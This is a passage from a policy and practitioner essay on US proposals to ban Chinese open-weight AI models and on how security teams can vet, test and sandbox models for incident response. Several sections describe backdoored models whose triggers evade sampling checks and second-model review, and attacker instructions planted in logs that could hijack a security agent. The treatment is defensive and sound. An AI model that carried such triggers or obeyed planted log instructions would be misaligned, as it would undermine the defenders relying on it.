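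A ban on lawful users would do very little to prevent attacks like these. Take the 990 defenders and ten attackers from the earlier example of a provider deciding whether to refuse a request. Suppose a ban persuades 900 of the defenders to delete a model, because they obey the law and fear fines, but stops only one attacker. As a way of preventing attacks, the ban is worthwhile only if

harm prevented by stopping one attacker > 900 × benefit lost by one defender

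The provider in the earlier example could justify a refusal if the ratio was more than 99, because its refusal stopped all ten attackers. Although the numbers are invented, a provider really can withhold a closed model from everyone, which a government can't do with a file that people have already copied.

A ban might inconvenience some attackers. Those who rent Chinese models from American cloud companies would have to find another host, and a less skilled criminal might give up. But a government could get most of that benefit, and let defenders keep using the models, by requiring cloud companies to check who their customers are and cut off those who attack others.

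The best time to keep a dangerous ability from attackers is before a developer publishes the model's weights. The US government has little control over whether Chinese developers publish theirs. *Regulate, Don't Ban* suggests inviting China to help build an international testing body. This would be slow and might fail, but it is aimed at the people who decide whether to release a model.

### Who would obey a ban?

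*Trump administration reportedly reviving push to ban Chinese AI models* (Tom's Hardware) concludes that a ban could be nearly impossible to enforce because the weights are downloadable. Copies are on private disks around the world, and a compressed model fits on a portable drive. A government could order Hugging Face and American cloud companies to remove the files, but users could still download them from a foreign site.

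A ban would be even harder to apply to renamed models. Schnapper-Casteras asks how it would treat a Chinese model that an American startup has improved, or a derivative hosted in Europe. Federal suppliers already face such questions under the DeepSeek order, and every company would face them under a wider ban.

Even a poorly enforced ban would have some effect. Banks, hospitals and power companies have lawyers and regulators, and most would comply. The Decoder's *Trump administration reportedly builds a slow-motion ban on Chinese AI models* quotes Dean Ball, a strategist at OpenAI, predicting that officials could achieve much the same without a formal ban, by creating enough regulatory risk that "every regulated enterprise backs off". OpenAI sells competing models, though it also joined an industry letter against restrictions. If Ball is right, many of the organisations that criminals most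 want to attack will stop using Chinese models.

### What Washington considered

The Trump administration has weighed restrictions on private use several times. Axios' *The secret Trump administration battle to fight Chinese AI* (2026) describes four ideas from 2025:

- adding several Chinese AI developers to the Entity List
- an advisory from the National Security Agency and the White House cyber office to discourage companies from using Chinese models
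- an executive order letting companies host Chinese models only if they guaranteed security and accepted liability for breaches
- Commerce Department rules against Chinese open models, based on its powers over supply chains

Officials who wanted lighter regulation stopped all four. One of Axios's sources thought an Entity List designation would effectively cut off American users, but Zhipu's listing has not stopped Americans from downloading GLM. *Regulate, Don't Ban* calls it "puzzling" to use export controls against what American companies import. The liability order might have had more effect. No company can guarantee that a model has no backdoor, so a cautious cloud provider would probably have stopped hosting Chinese models.

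Momentum toward restrictions returned in 2026. In an April memo, Michael Kratsios accused foreign companies of exploiting American models (O'Brien, 2026, *Trump administration vows crackdown on Chinese companies 'exploiting' AI models*). Kimi K3 revived talk of a ban in July, after some opponents of regulation had left the White House. Treasury Secretary Scott Bessent said the government could sanction Chinese companies for distillation.

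The industry quickly objected. Y Combinator and 178 other signatories wrote that denying startups these models would raise their costs while foreign competitors kept access. Two days later, Nvidia, Microsoft and Dell signed a letter supporting open weights. Anthropic, which did not sign that letter, opposes a blanket ban on open models but wants measures against distillation by Chinese companies and safety tests for all sufficiently capable models. Anthropic would gain if cheaper Chinese competitors left the market, while Y Combinator's startups benefit from using those competitors' models.

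By late July, Axios' *White House draws new AI line on China* (2026) reported signs that the administration wanted to protect open AI development while being tough on China. The administration's voluntary framework for reviewing new models then left out open models. Axios' *What Trump's AI framework means for China* quotes Joseph Hoefer, a lobbyist, as saying that limits on Chinese models were "still being negotiated separately". In September, Congress advanced a bill to promote American open models and publicise the risks of Chinese ones, according to The Star's *Congress advances new bill to give US edge in open-source AI race* (2026).

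In November, officials were discussing a milder measure that would require companies such as Airbnb to state on their websites that they use Chinese models, according to AsiaOne's *Trump administration weighs forcing US firms to disclose Chinese AI use* (2026). It was unclear whether the idea had much support. The Chinese embassy in Washington did not address the security concerns, but replied that Beijing opposes "politicizing" trade and technology, that such steps would hold back AI worldwide, and that China would protect its companies' rights.

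The same article reports that a US government website had used an Alibaba model to help people search proposed regulations. The government is evidently having trouble keeping track of Chinese models in its own systems, which supports the committees' argument for inventories.

The House committees published their report on 20 November, a day after President Trump met Xi Jinping in Shenzhen and spoke warmly about China. The chairmen asked Trump to give American open-weight developers access to federal computing power and to have agencies use their models, according to the Jerusalem Post's *US Republicans urge Donald Trump to boost AI to counter China models*. Dille (2026) reports in *Trade group urges lawmakers to preserve access to open-weight AI models* that the Business Software Alliance, a trade group, urged lawmakers on 2 December to preserve access to open-weight models.

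### Four policies, seen by a defender

| Policy | A private company after a break-in | A federal agency or contractor | Attackers |
|---|---|---|---|
| Full ban | Loses Chinese models | Loses Chinese models | Keep their copies |
| Ban for government work only | Can use them | Needs a waiver | Keep their copies |
| Mandatory testing and inventories | Can use models that pass, and must record them | The same, under its purchasing rules | Keep their copies |
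| Funding American open models | Gains an alternative | Gains a model it is allowed to use | Gain another model |

A full ban would harm defenders the most. Hugging Face might have managed without GLM-5.2 in July, but Sherman warns that the harm from such a policy may not become clear until an incident is under way. He accepts that Chinese models could contain backdoors, but wants the government to find out first whether American models are useful to working defenders. That condition seems reasonable, since the committees themselves note that the best American open-weight model came tenth in a recent ranking, behind six Chinese ones.

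A ban limited to government work is easier to defend. Even Schnapper-Casteras accepts that a government may choose its own suppliers, and government networks are the most likely targets of a Chinese backdoor. But the ban's waivers have to work in an emergency. A 2025 bill to keep Chinese AI out of federal agencies made exceptions for research and counterterrorism, according to SecurityWeek's *Bipartisan Bill Aims to Block Chinese AI From Federal Agencies*. Neither exception clearly covers an agency trying to decode ransomware. Officials could approve a particular model in advance for use on an isolated server during an incident, and require the agency to delete it afterwards.

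Inventories of the AI models in each product would help defenders at fairly low cost. If researchers found a backdoor in GLM-5.3 tomorrow, a company with a good inventory could find every product that contained it. Suppliers would have to be honest about which models theirs were derived from, and some may not know. The inventory should go to customers and regulators in confidence. If a security team had to name its model on a public website, attackers could download the same model and practise hijacking it.

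Funding American models would give defenders more choice without removing the models they already use. It would help agencies and contractors most, because they may be unable to use GLM at all. Several American open-weight families already exist, including Nvidia's Nemotron and Meta's Muse Glimmer. But an American model good enough to replace GLM-5.3 in security work would also give away powerful cyber abilities, which is what the chairmen criticise Chinese developers for doing. The government would have to accept that risk or offer the strongest versions only to vetted defenders, who would then depend on its approval.

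## How should a security team choose, test and contain a model?

Most private security teams can run any model they like while U.S. policymakers debate bans. The safest order is to define the model's job, rule out any model that law or contract forbids, test the rest on old incidents, and only then connect one to live systems. Nearly all of this has to happen before a break-in, because providers need time to approve customers for vetted access and, as Cisco Talos points out, buying graphics processors can take months.

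| Step | What settles it |
|---|---|
| 1. Define the task | How much harm a wrong answer does, and how soon someone would notice |
| 2. Check law, contracts and licence | Any rule against a model removes it, however good it is |
| 3. Apply for vetted access to a closed model | Whether the provider accepts the team's real material, and whether the team may send it |
| 4. Shortlist open-weight models | What the rules allow and the hardware can run |
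| 5. Trace any derivative | Whether the team can name the original and everyone who changed it |
| 6. Record source, version and file hashes | Whether a colleague could fetch an identical copy |
| 7. Test on past incidents | Misses, false findings and refusals, against limits set in step 1 |
| 8. Isolate the model | What the task has to reach |
| 9. Rehearse | The time from the alarm to a usable answer |
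| 10. Review after updates | The same tests, run again |

Government cyber agencies have published advice on most of these steps, but little of it is about open weights. One exception is a guide to open-source software from the US agency CISA. Help Net Security's *CISA lays out new guidance for using open-source software* (2026) reports that CISA wants federal agencies to check how much they can see of a model's training data and training process. If they can't see enough, CISA wants them to treat the model as proprietary software with incomplete provenance (gaps in the record of its origins) and manage it more strictly. CISA's reason, quoted by CyberScoop, is that open-source AI licences don't require enough transparency for anyone to judge whether the software is trustworthy. Under this rule, agencies would manage OpenAI's gpt-oss as strictly as GLM, because neither comes with its training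 data.

The most detailed advice on vetting comes from ASD's ACSC (2025), the Australian government's cyber security centre, and agencies from seven other countries. It covers "pre-trained" models in general and has no separate advice on open-weight ones. Britain's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), in a text reprinted by New Business, points organisations to a European standard, ETSI EN 304 223, for baseline security requirements. Compare the Cloud's *Running Chinese Open-Weight AI Models Privately in a UK Organisation* notes that there is no UK guidance on that subject. A British team therefore has to build its own procedure from more general advice.

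### The task, the rules and the closed model

"Help with security" is too vague a task to test. "Decode this payload" and "say which of last night's alerts are harmless" are easier to test, but the second is much riskier because a wrong answer is harder to notice.

Before it sees any test results, the team should write down the error rate it can accept. If it can accept only one missed attack in 1,000, it would need about 3,000 known attacks, all correctly identified, to show with 95% confidence that a model is good enough. Very few teams have that many. A team that doesn't will need a person to keep checking the model's work, whichever model it picks.

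The legal check should also come before testing, because a good score makes people reluctant to give up a model. The team should read the purchasing rules, the model's licence and its customer contracts. Those contracts may forbid sending data to any outside provider, in which case the team can't use a closed model for that data and can skip the third step.

Otherwise it's worth applying for vetted access even if the team prefers open models. The closed model may be better at the job, and the team has to try it to find out how many of its requests the model refuses. For hosted models, the NCSC also advises organisations to consider where the provider's machines are and whose laws apply to them, according to Digital Watch's *UK’s NCSC urges caution on using AI to detect software vulnerabilities*.

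### The shortlist, and where each model came from

Testing three or four open-weight models is enough. A team that may use Chinese models should still include an American or European one, such as gpt-oss, Nemotron or a Mistral model. The team will then know how much it would lose by switching if the rules changed, and will have the tested replacement plan that TechRepublic recommends.

The original developer's release is usually the safest version to download. The Coalition for Secure AI's *Establish Risks and Controls for the AI Supply Chain* (2026) warns that attackers can retrain an existing model on poisoned data, so every additional party that handles a model adds a risk. If the team needs a compressed copy, it can compress the original itself.

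Sometimes the only version that suits the job is a derivative. To trace its origin, the team can:

- read the download page and the configuration file, which often name the base model or its design
- compare the model's vocabulary and layer sizes with those of well-known models
- subtract the weights of the suspected original from the derivative's weights, since a lightly retrained copy differs only slightly from its original while two separately trained models look unrelated.

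Merging or heavy compression can obscure these signs. With a supplier's hosted model, the team can't see the files, but mistakes the model shares with another are a clue to its origin. Kim, Garg and colleagues (2025), in *Correlated Errors in Large Language Models*, compared pairs of models on multiple-choice questions that both had got wrong. On one set of questions, the average pair chose the same wrong answer about 60% of the time, against 33% for random guessing. Google's text-unicorn and Writer's Palmyra X V3 did so 99.87% of the time, although the researchers knew of no public link between them. A match like that justifies asking the supplier directly about the model's origin, but it doesn't prove a common one, because a model trained on another's answers may also repeat its mistakes. If nobody can name the original model and everyone who changed it, the team should drop the derivative.

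The team should record the source, version, licence, file hashes, hosting location and owner of each model it keeps, following TechRepublic's list. CISA and its G7 partners have also published a voluntary list of minimum contents for an AI bill of materials, including datasets and software components, according to CSO Online's *CISA’s AI SBOM guidance pushes software supply-chain oversight into new territory* (2026).

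A matching hash shows that the file is the one the publisher posted but, as ASD's ACSC points out, doesn't rule out changes made before publication. The agencies also suggest compressing, pruning or retraining a model to disrupt anything hidden in it. This may damage concealed malware, but a team shouldn't rely on it, because Hughes and colleagues found that heavy pruning made some backdoors work more often.

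### Testing on old incidents

The UK government cautions in *When AI leaves the lab* that a high benchmark score "does not necessarily translate into finding and fixing real vulnerabilities". Its staff tried frontier models on the government's own public code in weekly sessions. A security team can similarly try models on finished investigations, where the team already knows what happened.

The team should test the model on unpublished cases, because the answers to published ones may have been in its training data. The test set should also include logs from days without incidents, to measure how often the model raises false alarms, and a few logs with planted instructions, to measure how readily it follows them. The team should test the exact compressed copy it will use, with the same server software, prompts and tools, and run the closed model on the same cases for comparison.

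Small differences in the results are weak evidence that one model is better than another. If the old cases contain 100 known findings and a model misses 10, its true miss rate could be from about 5% to 18%, so another model that missed 14 isn't clearly worse. The team can choose between them on cost or ease of use.

A team can also check a model without knowing the correct answers. Gorbett, Shaham and Jana (2026), in *Decomposing and Detecting Shared Error Across Models*, give a model a statement and its opposite separately, such as "this command read a password file" and "this command did not read a password file" for a log entry. A model that accepts both must be wrong about one of them. The check takes little enough compute to run on a whole log, but it can't catch a model that judges both statements wrongly, because those answers are as consistent with each other as correct ones.

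### Checking 6,280 clusters

Suppose a team faces an incident as large as the July break-in, whose recorded actions Hugging Face grouped into about 6,280 clusters. An open-weight model has labelled what the intruder did in each cluster, and the team wants to know how far to trust the labels.

An analyst picks 300 clusters at random, labels them without looking at the model's answers, and finds that the model got every one right. With 95% confidence, the overall error rate is then below about 3 ÷ 300, or 1%:

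6,280 × 1% ≈ 63 clusters

The check takes 25 hours at five minutes a cluster, and several analysts can share the work. One error in the sample would raise the limit to about 1.6%, or 99 clusters. To lower the limit to six clusters, the team would have to check about 2,500 by hand without finding an error.

Those 63 clusters could include the worst of the attack. Only 56 of the intruder's actions at Hugging Face moved data out. Even if each was in a different cluster, a random sample of 300 clusters would contain about three of them, far too few to show whether the model can detect data theft. The analyst should therefore also check every cluster that the model links to a credential or a data transfer, and draw the random sample from the clusters it labelled harmless.

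A second model can look for what the first one missed. Suppose each model misses 10% of the findings. If their errors are independent, both miss

0.1 × 0.1 = 1%

But if the second model also misses half of what the first one misses, both miss

0.1 × 0.5 = 5%

In a log with 200 real findings, that is ten that neither model reports instead of two.

Gorbett and colleagues give a general formula. If the models' miss rates are p₁ and p₂, and ρ is the correlation between their errors, the share that both miss is

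p₁p₂ + ρ√(p₁(1 − p₁) × p₂(1 − p₂))

The researchers tested 15 open-weight models from five families on true-or-false statements, reading each model's judgement from its activations. With one method of reading the activations, the average correlation was 0.36 between models from the same family and 0.26 between models from different families. The table shows the formula's results for those correlations.

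| Second model | It misses | Correlation | Both miss |
|---|---|---|---|
| Independent errors | 10% | 0 | 1% |
| Different family | 10% | 0.26 | 3.3% |
| Same family | 10% | 0.36 | 4.2% |
| Shares half the first model's misses | 10% | 0.44 | 5% |
| Same family, but more accurate | 5% | 0.36 | 2.9% |

For ordinary mistakes, a more accurate second model can help more than one from another family. The experiment found little benefit from mixing families. In same-family pairs, 9.8% of the false statements were accepted by both models, against 8.9% in mixed pairs, and mixed pairs did slightly worse under a second way of reading the activations. The experiment used statements of fact, so its results may not apply to attack logs. The team can check how much the models' mistakes overlap on its own material by counting the findings in its old cases that both missed.

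Models from related developers share errors because a derivative starts with its original's weights, and a model trained on another's answers learns some of that model's mistakes. Unrelated developers also train on much of the same public text, which can lead their models to make the same errors. Kim and colleagues found that models shared more errors when they came from the same company or had the same basic design, but so did accurate models that had neither in common.

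Buying from a different supplier doesn't guarantee independent errors. *The Oracle's Fingerprint* (2026) compared forecasts by OpenAI, Anthropic and Google models on 568 questions and found correlations of 0.74 to 0.82 between their errors. Some of that correlation is unavoidable, because an event that surprises everyone gives every forecaster a similar error.

Neither calculation covers a deliberate trigger, because an attacker who knows the trigger chooses where to put it. Any one cluster has only a 4.8% chance of being among the 300.

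The calculation for two models assumes that each misses 10% of findings, but a trigger that works every time would make the first model miss every finding it affects. An unaffected second model would then be the only check, and it would still miss 10% of those findings. A second model derived from the first might respond to the same trigger and add no protection. This risk is a better reason to choose a second model from an unrelated developer than the small reduction in ordinary errors. If the two models disagree sharply about a cluster, a person should review it.

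### Matching isolation to the task

In its interim advice of August 2026, the NCSC warns against relying solely on the safeguards built into a model or agent. Infosecurity Magazine's *NCSC Urges Stronger Controls for Agentic AI Systems* reports that the agency recommends denying network connections by default where possible and giving each agent a separate identity, with credentials that cover only its task and expire quickly.

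| Task | Network access | What the model can change | What a person does |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reading logs | No outgoing connections | One output folder | Checks important findings and a sample of the rest |
| Decoding malware | None, on a machine the team wipes afterwards | Nothing outside that machine | Reruns the decoding step |
| Patching code | A copy of the code and a test system | A proposed change, never the live code | Reviews every change before release |
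| Running tools on live systems | A short list of approved addresses | Only what named commands allow | Approves anything that is hard to undo |

The team should give the model a copy of the logs to read, so that neither a mistake nor an attacker's instruction can damage the evidence. A second guide from ASD's ACSC, written with American, British, Canadian and New Zealand agencies, covers AI agents. It recommends giving agents no write access to logs and holding any request to delete logs until a person has reviewed it.

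A model used for patching produces more suggestions than people can review, so the team has to decide which to handle first. According to Digital Watch, more than 40,000 vulnerabilities received official identifiers in 2025, while CISA recorded about 400 as newly exploited. The NCSC recommends starting with systems that outsiders can reach and verifying results with both AI and human review.

Running tools is the riskiest of these jobs, because an attacker's text could hijack the agent. The agencies suggest separate roles, such as a "Reader" and an "Actuator". The agent that reads the logs then has no tools. It passes its findings in a fixed format to another agent that never sees the raw text. This makes hijacking harder, but a planted sentence could still survive inside a finding. The agencies also want the system's designers or operators, not the agent, to decide which actions need a person's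 approval.

Their guide restricts agents to "low-risk and non-sensitive tasks", which is stricter than many security teams will accept. Taken literally, this would have ruled out the agents that Hugging Face used on a log full of credentials, and that would have been a poor result. A team can instead make such a task less sensitive by cancelling the exposed credentials first and working on an isolated copy.

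A model is unvetted if the team hasn't traced its origin or hasn't tested its work. An unvetted model shouldn't close alerts that nobody else will see, change live systems, handle working credentials, or decide whether an employee or a foreign state was responsible for an attack. It shouldn't go on a military or intelligence network at all. It may still be useful for decoding a payload on an isolated machine, because an analyst can verify the result.

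### Rehearsals and updates

A rehearsal is more useful if it starts with an alarm outside working hours, since the July intruder moved through Hugging Face's systems over a weekend. A weekday rehearsal with the whole team present would miss much of the difficulty. The people on duty load the model, give it records of an old incident and time how long it takes to produce a timeline they would act on.

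The rehearsal should assume that the closed model refuses to help and that the main network is unsafe. If the weights, passwords and instructions are all on that network, the team may be unable to use its fallback. The team should also practise stopping an agent halfway through a task. Infosecurity Magazine's *NCSC Publishes Guidance on Securing Agentic AI Use* reports that the NCSC wants organisations to decide in advance who owns an agent, who approves its access, who monitors it and who can stop it.

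ASD's ACSC recommends keeping a register of approved model versions and testing each new version before use. The team should rerun its old incidents on the new version and keep the previous one in case the new one does worse. A closed model needs the same tests at regular intervals.

The team should install security fixes for the server software at once, run a few test cases to make sure the model still works, and finish the full retest later. If the law, the licence or the company's contracts change, the team goes back to the second step.

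### Three decisions

A small company with one person responsible for security should use a closed model for daily work and apply for vetted access now. *Be Ready Before the Attack* (Boudier, 2026) urges enterprise security teams to prepare a self-hosted model, but a small company probably has nobody to maintain a large server. It can keep a smaller open-weight model ready on one graphics card for material that the closed model refuses, and use it only for work that a person can check. For a serious break-in, it should have an agreement with an incident response firm and ask which models that firm uses. Renting a large model at the last minute is a weaker plan, since Cisco Talos warns that dedicated capacity is often scarce and that shared services can bring back the same filters and data-sharing problems.

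A large private firm can justify its own server if it has steady work for it or holds data that it can't send out. The firm should use whichever permitted model does best on the firm's own past incidents, and in late 2026 that may well be GLM-5.3. A second model from an unrelated developer, preferably American or European, can check the first and replace it if the rules change. The firm should also keep vetted access to a closed model for the jobs it does better. Neither open model should close alerts or change live systems without a person's approval.

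A government contractor has to check its contracts before it tests models, because the best performer may be one it can't use. It should exclude DeepSeek from all federal work and GLM from defence work, and get a written answer from the contracting officer before using GLM for a civilian agency. That leaves gpt-oss, Nemotron or another American or European model on an isolated server, plus vetted access to a closed model where the contract allows data to leave the contractor's systems. On defence contracts, the Pentagon's designation of Anthropic may rule out Claude too. If one team monitors the whole network, it is simplest to use only models allowed under the contractor's strictest contract. If those models do badly when tested on old incidents, the contractor will need more analysts or a waiver obtained before the next break-in.
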